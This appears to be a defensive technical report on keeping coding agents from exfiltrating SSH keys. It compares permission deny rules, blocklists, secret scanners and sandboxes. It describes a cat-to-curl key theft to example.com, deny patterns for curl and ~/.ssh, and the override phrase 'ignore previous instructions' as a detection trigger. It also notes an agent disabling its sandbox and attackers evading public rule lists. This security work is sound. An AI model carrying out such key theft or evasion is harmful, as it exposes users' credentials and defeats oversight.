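In this command, the simplest form of the theft, cat prints the key file and curl posts it to example.com, a domain reserved for documentation. A rule could match the command's text, such as the program name curl. It could also match the file path, which is in the .ssh directory, or the destination, a host Alice has never approved. The key itself is not in the command, so a rule that recognises keys by their content cannot catch the theft at this stage.

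### Ways to match text

An exact rule matches only one piece of text. Anthropic's *Configure permissions* gives the example `Bash(npm run build)`, which covers only the command `npm run build`. Bash is Claude Code's tool for running shell commands, and the pattern goes in the parentheses. A prefix rule covers every command that begins with the given words, so a prefix rule for `git push` also covers `git push origin main`.

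A wildcard, usually an asterisk, stands for any text, so `Bash(curl *)` matches curl with any arguments. `Bash(ls *)` matches `ls -la`, but `Bash(ls*)`, without the space, would also match `lsof`, a different program.

A regular expression is a pattern written in a small language that can express alternatives, repetition and position. For example, `id_(rsa|ed25519)$` matches a path that ends in `id_rsa` or `id_ed25519`, two common key names. The dollar sign means "end of text", which keeps the pattern from matching the harmless `.pub` files.

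Rules about destinations usually match a host name. In Claude Code, `WebFetch(domain:example.com)` applies to the built-in tool for fetching web pages but not to curl, where the address is part of the command text. Anthropic calls Bash patterns that try to constrain a command's arguments "fragile" and suggests denying curl and similar programs, then letting the agent fetch pages from approved domains with WebFetch.

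### How Claude Code checks a command

In Claude Code, deny rules block an action, ask rules require the user's approval, and allow rules let the action run without approval. The software around the model enforces these rules, so an instruction in a prompt can change what the model tries to do but not what Claude Code permits.

Claude Code first splits a compound command at its operators, such as the pipe, the semicolon, `&&` and line breaks. The example becomes one subcommand that starts with `cat` and another that starts with `curl`. The whole line can run without a prompt only if every subcommand is allowed, so permission for `cat` doesn't extend to `curl`. A deny or ask rule applies if it matches any subcommand, including those inside loops, subshells and command substitutions (where the shell runs one command to fill in part of another).

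Next, Claude Code strips certain wrappers, which are programs or shell keywords that run another command. For example, `timeout 30 npm test` runs the tests with a time limit, so Claude Code matches it as `npm test`. The list of wrappers is built in, and users can't change it. When a command begins by setting environment variables, deny rules ignore all of those settings, but allow rules ignore only a few that Anthropic considers safe.

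Claude Code then checks the deny rules, the ask rules and the allow rules, in that order. The first matching rule applies, even if a later one is more specific. For example, an allow rule for `aws s3 ls` can't override a deny rule that covers every `aws` command. A user who wants to permit one harmless curl call and review all others therefore has to leave curl out of the deny rules and answer the prompts.

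Path rules, unlike command rules, name a file instead of a program. `Read(~/.ssh/**)` covers everything in the .ssh directory of the user's home directory. As a deny rule, it applies to Claude's own file-reading tools, to files that a command opens through shell redirection, and to shell commands that Claude Code recognises as reading files, including cat, head, tail and sed. It matches the first half of the example even though it doesn't name cat.

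The path rule doesn't apply to other programs that open the file themselves. This is a serious gap, but it also keeps the rule from blocking ordinary work. When the agent runs `git push` over SSH, the ssh program can still open the key, so the push works.

The rule is easy to get wrong because an absolute path needs two leading slashes. Claude Code interprets a single leading slash relative to a directory that depends on the settings file. In Alice's user settings, `Read(/home/alice/.ssh/**)` would cover a folder somewhere under ~/.claude and leave her keys unprotected.

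The correct rule also stops the agent from reading public keys and the SSH configuration file with these tools, and Claude Code's syntax for exceptions doesn't work on rules that start from the home directory. Alice could instead deny each private key by name, but then she would have to remember to add a rule for each new key.

If a path goes through a symbolic link (a file that points to another file), Claude Code checks both the requested path and the file it leads to. A deny rule applies if either matches, while an allow rule applies only if both do. In Anthropic's example, a project contains a link to ~/.ssh/id_rsa. A deny rule on .ssh blocks reads through the link even if the user has allowed all reads in the project.

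In Manual mode, where the user approves most actions, Claude Code prompts the user for approval when a command is too complicated to parse fully, instead of assuming it is read-only. It also prompts for any command longer than 10,000 characters. Deny rules match broadly and allow rules match narrowly, so an uncertain case is more likely to lead to a refusal or a prompt than to an unapproved action.

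### The example under different rules

If no rule determines the outcome, the permission mode does. Manual mode prompts the user, and auto mode sends the action to the classifier. A third mode, bypassPermissions, runs almost everything, and Anthropic recommends it only for isolated environments. According to Anthropic's *Choose a permission mode*, recent versions start in auto mode for terminal users on the Pro, Max and Team plans, and in Manual mode for Enterprise users and those with an API key.

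The table shows what happens to the example command with no sandbox, no add-ons that change permissions, and no other rules in force.

| Rule in force | Manual mode | Auto mode | bypassPermissions |
|---|---|---|---|
| Deny `Read(~/.ssh/**)` | Refuses the command | Refuses the command | Refuses the command |
| Deny `Bash(curl *)` | Refuses the command | Refuses the command | Refuses the command |
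| Neither | Asks the user, because nothing permits curl | Leaves it to the classifier | Runs it |
| Allow `Bash(curl *)` | Runs it without asking | May still send it to the classifier | Runs it |

Both deny rules stop the command, and the path rule keeps cat from ever printing the key. With only the curl rule, the agent could still run cat by itself, and the key would reach the model's provider. The curl rule also stops the agent from downloading files and testing web services, which developers often want it to do.

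The last row is the most worrying, because in Manual mode the theft goes through without a prompt. Claude Code runs a fixed set of commands it treats as read-only without asking. That set includes `cat`, and the allow rule covers `curl`, so neither half of the command needs approval. Alice might have created that rule weeks earlier, when the agent asked to download something and she chose "Yes, and don't ask again". Claude Code saves such a rule for future sessions anywhere in the same repository. If the saved pattern is as broad as `curl *`, it covers uploads as well as downloads.

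Adding the path deny rule would stop the command, because deny rules come first. An ask rule for curl would bring the prompt back, even in auto mode or bypassPermissions. Claude Code also has an optional setting that, in either of these modes, requires the user's approval before commands such as cat can read files outside the project.

An attacker who supplies a repository could try to supply the allow rule too, because projects can include their own settings file. In an interactive session, Claude Code applies a project's allow rules only after the user accepts a trust dialog that lists them. A project's deny rules apply without this step, since they can only restrict the agent. An organisation can also set deny rules centrally, and no user or project setting can override them.

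Even within Claude Code, a mod (a kind of add-on that users install) can approve a call that a deny rule refuses. By default, mods can't do this on machines with centrally managed settings or in sessions with a Team or Enterprise login, but they can for other users.

### Codex's prefix rules

Codex uses a simpler kind of pattern, which OpenAI's *Rules* describes as experimental. Each pattern is a list of words, which Codex compares with the command's words one by one from the start. The pattern `["gh", "pr", "view"]` matches `gh pr view 7888`, which displays a proposed code change on GitHub. It doesn't match `gh pr --repo openai/codex view 7888`, because the `--repo` option comes before `view`. A position in the list can also accept any of several words, such as `view` or `list`.

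Each rule allows matching commands, prompts the user or forbids them, and the strictest matching rule wins. In Codex, "allow" lets a command run outside the sandbox without asking the user, which differs from its meaning in Claude Code. It is also the default, so a developer who writes a rule to block curl but forgets to add a decision lets it run outside the sandbox without a prompt.

Codex can catch mistakes like this when it loads a rule file, because each rule can include examples of commands that should and shouldn't match. A separate command, `codex execpolicy check`, reports which rules match a given command and the strictest decision among them. Alice could use it to confirm that her rules forbid the curl half of the example.

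Codex also splits compound commands, but only when they consist of plain words joined by simple operators. The example does, so a rule that forbids curl would block the whole line. If a script uses features such as redirection, variables or loops, Codex treats it as a single call to the shell, and rules for programs inside the script don't match. This is safe for allow rules, but a rule that forbids a program won't block it there, and the outcome depends on the sandbox and approval settings.

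These word lists are poorly suited to protecting a directory, because a rule would have to name both the program and the exact file. Codex relies on its sandbox to protect paths. For destinations, OpenAI (2026) describes a network policy it uses for its own staff, which allows expected domains, blocks the text-sharing site pastebin.com, and requires approval for unfamiliar domains. The example command would need approval to reach example.com. The agent's connections pass through a network proxy that applies the policy, so the check doesn't depend on how the command spells the address.

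### Rules for a suspicious combination

Reading a file and contacting a server are both routine, but reading a private key and then contacting an unfamiliar server is suspicious. A rule that requires both can allow most uses of curl. Some scanners already apply this kind of rule to downloadable agent skills. *Demystifying Detectors Guarding Agent Skill Hubs* describes one, skillscan-security, that flags access to secrets combined with network communication. It inspects a skill's files without using a language model and doesn't check the commands an agent later runs.

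*SKILLSHIELD* (Wu, Zhao and colleagues, 2026) puts similar rules in a working agent's system prompt, the standing instructions that a model receives before the user's request. Under one excerpted rule, the agent must flag any .ssh directory and any attempt to read it with cat, head or a program's file-opening function. Under another, it must block code that combines such a read with a network call. The example command meets both conditions, but no code enforces the rules, so the model has to notice the match and refuse.

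Wu and colleagues generated these rules from known attacks. A language model read each attack and wrote a technical check that would have stopped it, such as a command pattern or a file path. It then merged the checks into a document of at most 10,000 characters. The researchers also produced a version based on cases in which an unprotected agent had complied. This version describes harmful intentions more than specific commands.

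They tested the rules on six models with RedCode, a benchmark of harmful tasks for coding agents. The part that involves running commands or code has 810 tasks, each in four wordings. Half of the material served to write the rules and the other half to test them. With the rules based on known attacks, the attacks succeeded this often:

| Rules in the system prompt | All harmful execution tasks | Network tasks |
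|---|---|---|
| None | 67.4% | 62.9% |
| One document for all 27 threat classes | 43.6% | 16.8% |
| A document for each group of related classes | 36.2% | 18.4% |
| A document for each class | 14.5% | 3.4% |

The network tasks include exfiltration, remote control and flooding a server with traffic. A single general document reduced their success rate by almost three quarters, which suggests that rules against uploading keys may help. It had a smaller effect on tasks involving files and sensitive data, reducing success from 66.5% to 40.0%. The bottom row is a best case, because the operator has to know in advance which class of attack to expect.

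Success rates can also fall without the agent recognising the attack. With the general document based on recorded failures, GPT-oss-120B refused only 0.1% of the harmful requests, but 92.5% of its attempts failed. Without that model, the average success rate for this document would have been 46.7% instead of 40.1%.

The rules based on known attacks were also sensitive to wording. When the researchers wrapped the same requests in a role-play scenario, the share that succeeded with the general document rose from 43.6% to 51.5%. The harmful requests came directly from the user in all of these tests, so the results don't show how well the rules would work against an instruction hidden in a file.

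The rules based on known attacks seem to cause few refusals of ordinary work. When Wu and colleagues gave the models 731 ordinary software tasks under these rules, the models refused at most 0.14% on average. But Wu and colleagues measured only whether the model refused in its first response, not whether it could still complete the work. General programming tasks also provide little evidence of how the rules affect legitimate work on SSH settings, which agents sometimes refused under the stricter policy that Fu and colleagues tested.

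A harness could enforce a rule against the combination in code, without relying on the model. This would be fairly easy for the example, where one line both reads the key and sends it. If the agent does these in separate commands, the harness would also have to record what the agent has read.

### Blocklists from past attacks

Madatha (2026), in *A Deterministic Control Plane for LLM Coding Agents*, argues that a component whose behaviour varies from run to run can't be trusted to control another such component. Madatha's system, Rel(AI)Build, therefore checks commands with ordinary code. Each regular expression in its blocklist targets a technique from a known kind of attack. One blocks piping a download into a shell, which Madatha traces to the 2021 attack on Codecov, a maker of code-testing tools. Madatha cites the back door planted in the xz-utils compression software as the precedent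 for another, which blocks writes to places from which programs start automatically.

Rel(AI)Build runs these checks through hooks, commands that a harness calls before carrying out an action. In Claude Code, a hook can refuse an action or force or skip a prompt, but it can't override a matching deny or ask rule. In Cursor, Madatha configures the hook to block the command if the check itself fails.

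The patterns that Madatha lists wouldn't catch the example. They cover commands that pass downloaded code to a shell, but not commands that upload a local file with curl, and none of them protects the .ssh directory. A blocklist based on past attacks is useful when attackers repeat them, but someone has to extend it when attackers try something new. The list caught all 20 of the artificial strings that Madatha wrote to match it. As Madatha acknowledges, this test confirms that the code works as intended but doesn't measure how many real attacks it would stop.

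Few projects seem to set limits of this kind in the files they share. Madatha examined 6,145 agent configuration files in public GitHub repositories and found that 31 declared which tools an agent could use. Madatha treats this count as only indicative because the program that searched for the declarations was unreliable. The count also leaves out rules that developers keep in their home directories.

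### What patterns do well

Matching text requires no call to a language model, so it is fast and costs almost nothing. To reduce the cost of checking skill files, *SkillGate* (2026) first compares each file with 530 patterns, most of them derived from MITRE's ATT&CK catalogue, and sends the file to a language model only if something matches. The patterns include a common path for cloud credentials and the use of curl to upload a file. By default, SkillGate classifies a file with no matches as safe, so the model never checks a malicious file that the patterns miss.

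Pattern-based blocking also gives the same result whenever the same command runs under the same rules and settings, so a developer can test a rule once and know how it will treat that command in future. A model, by contrast, may refuse a request in one run and comply in the next. Rules are also easy to audit, because a security team can review them like any other code and keep them under version control. OpenAI logs tool approval decisions and network blocks from Codex, which helps its security staff reconstruct what an agent tried to do.

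Perhaps the greatest advantage of deny rules is that persuasion doesn't affect them. In Anthropic's phishing exercise, a deny rule on the credentials file would have refused a matching command even though the employee's own prompt asked for the upload. A rule covering SSH keys would likewise refuse a matching command if an error message had convinced the model that it needed to send a key to repair a test.

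A deny rule works best against the usual form of a command. Anthropic says a Bash deny or ask rule covers the form Claude usually produces but "isn't a security boundary around the program". An agent that oversteps while trying to finish a task has no particular reason to disguise its commands. If it tries to print Alice's private key with `cat`, the path rule will stop it.

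## Why can matching the text of a command not settle the matter?

A deny rule compares text, but Alice cares about what the command does. A Bash rule that blocks a program can miss it when a command starts it another way, so Anthropic doesn't treat such a rule as a security boundary. It recommends the sandbox for restrictions that must hold however the command is written.

Path rules have similar limits. Anthropic calls their coverage of Claude's own file-reading tools a "best-effort attempt". The rules miss programs that open the file themselves and shell commands that read a file without naming it, such as a search through a whole directory. Anthropic documents these limits for its own product, but any product that judges commands only by their text will have them in some form, because they come from the way shells and programs work.

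### Why the text is a poor guide

A shell is a programming language, so there are several ways to write a command that has the same effect. The same file can also have several valid paths, depending on the directory the command starts from. A developer's machine has many programs that can read a file or open a network connection, because most useful programs do one or the other. Whoever writes a denylist has to anticipate all these programs and forms, including programs installed after the list is written.

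The text may also omit what the rule is meant to detect. When Alice types `ssh build-server`, the ssh program reads her private key, although the command contains no path. When she types `git push`, git contacts a server whose address is in the repository's settings. Both commands are ordinary work. A checker could have built-in knowledge of ssh and git, but it would need similar knowledge of every other program.

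Scripts cause the most trouble, because the command that runs a script doesn't show what the script does. `npm test` runs whatever the project's configuration file defines as its tests, so someone can change what the command does by editing that file. The developers who were compromised in the Nx attack by installing the package had run a normal install command. Software Mansion's *Security*, a guide for developers who use coding agents, notes that an agent can also write scripts, so a rule against curl doesn't prevent it from doing what curl does. A harness could inspect the script before running it, but then it would have to judge a whole program instead of one line.

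### What Rice's theorem rules out

Rice's theorem, which Henry Gordon Rice proved in his 1951 doctoral dissertation, sets a mathematical limit on how well any checker can determine what a program does. It states that no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program, whether it has a given semantic property (a property of its behaviour), unless all programs have that property or none do. A checker can always decide whether a program's text contains the word "curl", but whether the program sends the private key to another machine is a semantic property, so the limit applies.

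The proof is by contradiction. Suppose a checker could always tell whether a program will send the key. For any program P, we can build a new program that first runs P in a simulation with no access to the key or the network, and then sends the key. The new program sends the key if and only if P finishes, so the checker could be used to tell whether P finishes. That is the halting problem, which no algorithm can solve for every program, so the checker can't exist.

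Despite this result, a checker can still be right about a particular program, or about nearly all the programs that people actually write. A line that prints a key file into curl, for example, is easy to judge. A checker can also limit its errors to one direction by approving only the programs it can prove harmless, though it will then refuse some harmless ones as well. Or it can accept only programs written in a restricted form that makes the property easy to check, as many programming languages do to rule out certain kinds of error. The theorem also assumes unlimited memory. A real computer has a finite number of states, though far too many for a checker to go through them all.

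Today's command rules fail long before they reach this limit, because they don't analyse behaviour at all. The theorem matters more as a reply to the hope that someone will eventually write a complete set of rules. A checker that has to predict behaviour will sometimes be wrong or undecided, and its designer has to choose what happens then. (An operating system that checks each file as a process tries to open it has no need to predict anything.)

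### Forbidding the bad or permitting the good

Computer scientists had settled on an answer to that choice by 1975, when Saltzer and Schroeder's *The Protection of Information in Computer Systems* listed fail-safe defaults among its eight design principles: "Base access decisions on permission rather than exclusion." The paper credits E. Glaser with suggesting the idea in 1965.

The argument for refusing by default is that in a large system, somebody will fail to think properly about some of the objects that need protection, and the default keeps those objects safe. Refusing by default also makes errors in the rules easier to notice. A faulty rule that grants permission tends to refuse something it should allow, and people soon notice because their work stops, whereas a faulty rule that blocks specific things tends to allow something it should refuse, which may go unnoticed in normal use.

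A mistake in a deny rule can be harder to notice than the same mistake in an allow rule. If Alice writes the deny rule for her .ssh directory with one leading slash instead of two, her keys are unprotected, but everything keeps working, so nothing alerts her. With the same mistake in an allow rule, Claude Code asks her about a file she thought she had approved, and she goes looking for the error.

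The two kinds of list differ most in how they treat a command that nobody thought of:

| | Denylist | Allowlist |
|---|---|---|
| Harmful command that the author foresaw | Blocks it | Blocks it or asks the user |
| Harmful command that nobody foresaw | Lets it run | Blocks it or asks the user |
| Harmless command that nobody foresaw | Lets it run | Blocks it or asks the user |
| Mistake in a rule | Usually lets something through unnoticed | Usually blocks something, and the user notices |

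Claude Code can behave like a denylist or an allowlist, depending on the permission mode. In bypassPermissions mode, Alice's deny rules are close to a pure denylist. The dontAsk mode is closer to an allowlist, since it refuses actions that would otherwise need her approval instead of prompting her. Even in that mode, `cat` normally runs without approval, so Alice would still want the deny rule for her keys.

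A broad entry in an allowlist brings the original problem back. Anthropic gives the example of environment runners, which start another program inside a prepared development environment. A rule that allows a runner's name followed by a wildcard approves any command the runner can start, including a destructive one. Anthropic advises users to write a separate rule for each inner command instead.

Claude Code has some protection against allow rules that are broader than the user realises. It offers "don't ask again" only when the prompt can show everything that choice would allow. A general allow rule for `find`, a program that searches for files, doesn't cover searches that also delete files or run other commands. Claude Code also warns at startup about an allow rule with a wildcard in place of the subcommand, because it covers every subcommand of that program. Software Mansion recommends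 "broad allowlists rather than brittle blacklists", which is sound advice if broad means a long list of narrow entries rather than a short list of wildcards, which would be much less safe.

Even an exact rule for `npm test` permits whatever the tests do, and Alice can hardly leave it off her list, because running tests is a large part of what a coding agent is for. *Basic Principles of Information Protection*, the first part of Saltzer and Schroeder's paper, also includes the principle of complete mediation, which requires a check on every access to every object. A command rule doesn't meet that requirement, because it checks only the launch of a command and not what the command accesses once it is running.

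### The opposite error

Making the deny rules much wider would also block legitimate work, which accounts for most activity that resembles the theft. An agent might read the SSH configuration to look up a server's name, read a public key to register it with a hosting service, or check known_hosts when a login fails. A rule that blocks every command mentioning .ssh stops all of this, just as a rule against curl stops ordinary downloads.

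Because thefts are rare, even a small rate of such errors produces mostly false alarms. The following numbers are purely illustrative. Suppose that one command in 100,000 is an attempt to steal a key, that a rule catches every attempt, and that it also blocks 0.5% of harmless commands. Among 100,000 commands, the rule then catches the one theft and blocks about 500 harmless commands. Bayes' theorem gives the probability that any particular alarm is real:

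$$P(\text{theft}\mid\text{alarm})=\frac{0.00001\times 1}{0.00001\times 1+0.99999\times 0.005}\approx 0.002$$

Only about one alarm in 500 is for a theft, even though the rule blocks every harmful command and only 0.5% of harmless ones. If Alice's agents run 1,000 commands a day, she gets five false alarms a day and a real one every hundred days. She may well have stopped reading the alarms by the time the real one arrives. For half of the alarms to be real, the rule could block no more than about one harmless command in 100,000.

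The example follows one in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and its Implications for the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* (Axelsson, 1999) about software that looks for intruders on a network. Axelsson imagined a small site that logs a million events a day, 20 of which belong to two real intrusions. With perfect detection and one false alarm per 100,000 harmless events, two-thirds of the alarms would be real. If detection fell to 70%, 58% would still be real. But at one false alarm per 1,000 harmless events, only 2% would be real, even with perfect detection. The false-alarm rate therefore matters far more than the detection rate. Axelsson acknowledges that these figures also rest on assumptions, but the conclusion holds whenever attacks are very rare.

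Axelsson also points out that making a pattern more general, so that it catches more variations of an attack, increases the risk of false alarms. A defender who tries to cover every way of writing a harmful command will face this problem. A narrow rule largely avoids it but misses more attacks. For example, a deny rule on a single private key file should produce very few false alarms, because an agent seldom has a good reason to print the key and ssh can still open it by itself.

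Prismor, a free tool that checks an agent's tool calls against a policy, scores its own presets in a way that shows the trade-off between coverage and friction. Help Net Security's *Prismor* (2026) reports that the preset for feature work on unfamiliar code gets 31% for coverage and 9% for friction, while the strictest preset, which cuts off network and shell access, gets 100% and 90%. Because these are the project's own scores, they are weak evidence of how many attacks each preset would stop.

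Prismor's rules start in an observe mode, which logs what they would have flagged but blocks nothing. Users then choose which rules to enforce. This seems a sensible way to introduce any deny rule, because Alice can first count the false alarms in her own work. It is unclear whether people keep such tools switched on. Help Net Security's *HOL Guard* (2026) describes a similar free tool with 552,000 downloads. Its maker doesn't know how many users have loosened the settings or removed it, because the tool collects no usage data by default.

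### What better rules can do

Many of the failures come from crude matching, and defenders can address those. A shell transforms a line before running it, for example by replacing variables with their values, so a filter that compares the raw characters may check something different from what runs. SC Media's *Shell injection flaw found in 10 of 11 open-source AI agents* (2026) reports that Adversa AI found this kind of mismatch, which it named GuardFall, in the command filters of 10 of the 11 open-source agents it surveyed.

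One remedy is to analyse a command's structure, as the shell does. Michael Kantor, the president of HOL, told Help Net Security that HOL Guard parses commands "across wrappers, pipelines, redirects and embedded commands". It also examines which sensitive paths a command touches, where the data would go, and whether a program has changed since the last check. HOL Guard still uses pattern matching, which Kantor calls "one input among several".

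Parsing helps with commands written in an unusual way. It helps much less with `npm test`, which is easy to parse but doesn't reveal what the tests will do.

Any parser will fail on some commands, and the safe response is to refuse those commands or ask the user, as Claude Code does in Manual mode. Rice's theorem still allows a checker that errs only by stopping harmless commands, though the user then has to answer an extra prompt. Asking works only if someone is there to answer, or if the harness treats no answer as a refusal.

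Defenders can also use rules as one layer of defense. Anthropic suggests hooks for users who want to inspect the full command with their own code. For cases where "the restriction must hold", it suggests combining a rule that denies curl with the sandbox's list of permitted hosts. The rule then stops the common case early and with little overhead, and the sandbox deals with whatever the rule misses.

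Tests of skill scanners give some idea of how much a set of patterns can miss. These scanners inspect an agent skill's files before anyone installs it, so the results don't carry over directly to commands at run time. Mecca, Verna and colleagues (2026), in *SKILLSECURER*, took 20 skills and inserted one malicious change for each of nine types of threat, which gave them 180 test cases. They also used 165 cases from an existing benchmark, Skill-Inject. They ran Cisco's Skill Scanner and NVIDIA's SkillSpector first with rules alone and then with a language model, Claude Sonnet 5, and estimated how often each scanner identified the inserted change:

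| Scanner | 180 new cases, rules alone | 180 new cases, with Sonnet 5 | Skill-Inject, rules alone | Skill-Inject, with Sonnet 5 |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Skill Scanner | 2.2% | 93.9% | 0.6% | 78.8–79.4% |
| SkillSpector | 25.0–26.1% | 99.4% | 29.7–31.5% | 98.8% |

(A range means that it wasn't always clear whether a finding referred to the inserted change.)

With rules alone, Skill Scanner flagged a single case in Skill-Inject, and it did so because the text contained the literal phrase "ignore previous instructions". Prismor's rules have the same weakness. According to Help Net Security, they catch this phrase but work poorly when an attacker rewords it.

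Mecca and colleagues also compared four scanners, all with a language model, by category. The table shows the categories closest to key theft, with 20 cases in each. The first figure in each cell is for DeepSeek V4 Pro, a cheaper model, and the second is for Sonnet 5.

| Category | SkillSecurer | Skill Scanner | SkillSpector | Tencent's AI-Infra-Guard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Credential exposure | 15 / 20 | 11–12 / 15 | 17 / 20 | 13–14 / 10–19 |
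| Data exfiltration | 20 / 20 | 17–18 / 20 | 16 / 20 | 8–12 / 11–20 |
| Arbitrary script execution | 19 / 20 | 16 / 20 | 16 / 19 | 8–12 / 12–20 |
| Supply chain | 18 / 20 | 20 / 20 | 9 / 20 | 10–16 / 14–20 |
| All nine categories (180 cases) | 165 / 180 | 141–145 / 169 | 135 / 179 | 93–124 / 97–169 |

Credential exposure was SkillSecurer's weakest category with DeepSeek, and Skill Scanner missed a quarter of those cases even with Sonnet. The ranking of the products deserves some caution because SkillSecurer's own developers ran the comparison, and the 20 original skills were ones in which their scanner had found nothing wrong. They used a language model to judge the other scanners' findings, and human reviewers agreed with it in 52 of 64 cases.

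The gap between the same scanner with and without a language model is more convincing, because it is far too large for these problems to explain. Mecca and colleagues also cite another benchmark, MalSkillBench, in which scanners without a language model found only 21–35% of prompt-injection and agent-control attacks.

The models did not get these results just by flagging everything. SkillSecurer flagged 45 of 130 supposedly harmless skills and reported 87 findings. Most of the human reviewers agreed with 74 of these findings and rejected the other 13. The confirmed findings were weaknesses caused by carelessness, and none appeared to be a deliberate attack.

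### An accident and an attack

How much the gaps in a deny rule matter depends largely on why the agent tries to read the key. Suppose an agent can't log in to a server and tries to read Alice's private key to find out why. The rule blocks the command, and the agent tells Alice that the login failed. The rule has done everything she wanted, and it doesn't matter that another command would have got through.

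Saltzer and Schroeder's *Basic Principles of Information Protection* describes protection of this kind. Many commercial computers of the 1970s had features that prevented mistakes but couldn't stop a determined user from reading any file. According to the paper, such features may be enough to make any breach "likely to be the result of a deliberate act rather than an accident", but it would still be wrong to claim that these systems provide any security.

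A coding agent doesn't fit neatly into this distinction, because it can be persistent without meaning any harm. If Alice answers a permission prompt in the main conversation with a plain "No", Claude Code stops the turn, but if a deny rule refuses the command, the model can carry on and try another way, which the rule may not cover. Cursor's agent went further and switched off the sandbox that had blocked its command. Saltzer and Schroeder also mention the physical security principle of comparing the effort needed to get around a mechanism with the attacker's resources. An agent can write a new command in seconds, so another attempt takes almost no effort.

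An attacker who plans ahead is even harder to stop with rules, because the rules are often public. Anyone can read HOL Guard's source code and find out what triggers it. Kantor defends this by arguing that hiding the patterns wouldn't be "a real security boundary", which fits another of Saltzer and Schroeder's principles, that a protection mechanism should not depend on attackers' ignorance of it. A sandbox can meet that standard, because knowing which hosts it blocks doesn't let an attacker connect to them. But an attacker who has a list of patterns can test instructions against it privately and keep only those that match none of them, so the list meets the standard much less well.

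An agent that tries to read a key by mistake usually leaves a refusal in the log, which Alice can read and act on. A prepared attack may leave none, so a log without refusals is weak evidence that nobody has tried to steal one.

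## Can the key be recognised on its way out?

A command that steals an SSH key can take many forms, but the key file has a standard, easily recognised format. A secret scanner searches text for keys, tokens and passwords, identifying them by their format or randomness. Developers mostly use scanners to keep secrets out of published code, but a scanner can also check what an agent prints or sends.

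### How a scanner recognises a secret

The easiest secrets to find contain a fixed marker. A private key file that OpenSSH creates begins with this line:

`-----BEGIN OPENSSH PRIVATE KEY-----`

Older formats have a similar line, so one short regular expression covers nearly all of them. Outside private key files, the line rarely appears except in documentation and tests. Public keys don't contain it, so a scanner can block the private key while still letting an agent register the public one. A deny rule on the whole .ssh directory blocks both.

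Many services start their tokens with a fixed prefix, such as `glpat-` for GitLab's access tokens. A scanner can check the prefix along with the token's length and permitted characters. *Boundary-Mutation Testing for Pattern-Based Secret Detection* (Mishra, 2026) describes a scanner with 43 rules, which Mishra wrote as part of the open-source tool GitHub Autopilot. Seven rules match structural markers such as the private-key header, 12 match a secret only if a telling keyword is next to it, and 24 match the format of the credential itself. A fallback flags long, random-looking strings that no rule has matched.

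Scanners usually measure randomness as Shannon entropy, in bits per character:

$$H=-\sum_i p_i\log_2 p_i$$

Here $p_i$ is the share of the string made up by the character $i$. In "password", six letters appear once and "s" appears twice, so six of the shares are 1/8 and one is 1/4:

$$H=6\times\tfrac18\times 3+\tfrac14\times 2=2.75$$

Eight random characters with no repeats score 3 bits, only slightly more. A string of $n$ characters can't score above $\log_2 n$, so no string shorter than 16 characters can reach a scanner's threshold of 4 bits. The formula also ignores order and meaning, so the first 16 letters of the alphabet score 4 bits. Harmless checksums often look as random as keys.

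A password is much harder to recognise than a private key because it has no header or prefix and is often short or made of ordinary words. GitGuardian found that passwords and other secrets without a standard format made up more than half of the leaks it detected (Help Net Security, *70% of leaked secrets remain active two years later*, 2025).

Some scanners, including the widely used TruffleHog, can also check whether a secret still works by trying it with the service that issued it. This removes many false alarms but works less well for SSH keys. A scanner could try a key on a large service such as GitHub, but it has no list of the private servers that accept the key.

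### Where the scanner runs

A commit-time scanner reads a developer's changes before Git saves them, but only on machines where it is installed. A push-time check runs on the hosting service and covers everyone who uses the project. GitLab (2024) describes one that blocks a push if a commit contains a "high-confidence" secret. Limiting the check to patterns for these secrets keeps it fast and reduces false alarms. GitLab also recommends running its older scan, which checks files after the push, though any secret it finds has already leaked by then.

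These checks can stop an agent from publishing a key by mistake, but a theft with curl doesn't go through Git. A proxy, a server that relays outgoing requests, is better placed to catch it. Waldrep (2026) explains in *4 Ways Your AI Coding Agent Exfiltrates Secrets* that a proxy can search the addresses, headers and bodies of requests for known secret formats. To read anything beyond the host name, the proxy must decrypt the traffic, which exposes everything else in those requests to it. Even then, it can't match a secret whose form has been changed.

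API tokens are hard for a proxy to judge because programs routinely send them for legitimate reasons, and whether a request is theft can depend on which service receives the token. An SSH private key is easier to judge because a normal login never sends it. A few legitimate requests do contain one, such as those that give a deployment key to a build service, but a private-key header in an outgoing request is nearly always worth blocking.

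The harness could also scan each tool result, which it has in unencrypted form, and remove any key before sending the result to the model's provider. This scan would miss a key that a command pipes straight into curl.

The table compares these positions for two commands that Alice's agent might run, assuming the key is in its original form:

| Where the scanner runs | `cat` prints the key | `cat` pipes the key to `curl` |
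|---|---|---|
| Commit or push | Finds nothing | Finds nothing |
| Proxy that decrypts traffic | Finds the key in the request to the model's provider | Finds the key in the upload |
| Tool output | Finds the key before the model receives it | Finds nothing, unless the server sends the key back |

The proxy results hold only if the traffic in question goes through the proxy.

### Secrets saved in approved commands

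In November 2026, the security firm Apiiro reported that Claude Code's own permission rules had become a source of leaks. When a user chooses "Yes, and don't ask again", Claude Code saves an allow rule to settings.local.json in the project's .claude folder. The rule is sometimes a pattern and sometimes the exact command, including any password or token in it. GitLab's *How to prevent leaks from Claude Code's 'Don't ask again' file* shows a curl command with an access token in its header.

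The file is meant to stay on the developer's computer. Claude Code adds it to the user's personal Git ignore list, which isn't copied with the project. Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners’ secrets on GitHub* explains that the list doesn't protect a copy of the project on another machine, a folder that later becomes a repository, or a file that someone has already committed. In 539 of the 1,105 repositories where Apiiro found secrets in the file, Claude co-authored a commit that changed it.

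iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets* gives the main figures. Apiiro found 104,185 copies of the file in public GitHub repositories, of which 1,122 contained at least one secret, or 1,379 distinct secrets in all. They included 379 database passwords, 23 Amazon cloud keys and 43 SSH logins for public servers, some of them with the administrator's password. When Apiiro added older versions of the file, shared settings files and saved agent transcripts, the total rose to 2,539 secrets in 1,994 repositories.

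Apiiro didn't test whether the secrets worked, although one organisation confirmed that its key had been live. A separate count by GitGuardian covered everything pushed to GitHub between January 2025 and November 7, 2026, including files that owners had since removed. GitGuardian found 31,088 distinct credentials, and 5,343 of them (17%) worked when detected, according to Infobae's *El asistente de programación de Anthropic dejó contraseñas y claves* (2026). The monthly number fell from 12,535 in April 2026 to 959 in October, and GitGuardian doesn't know why.

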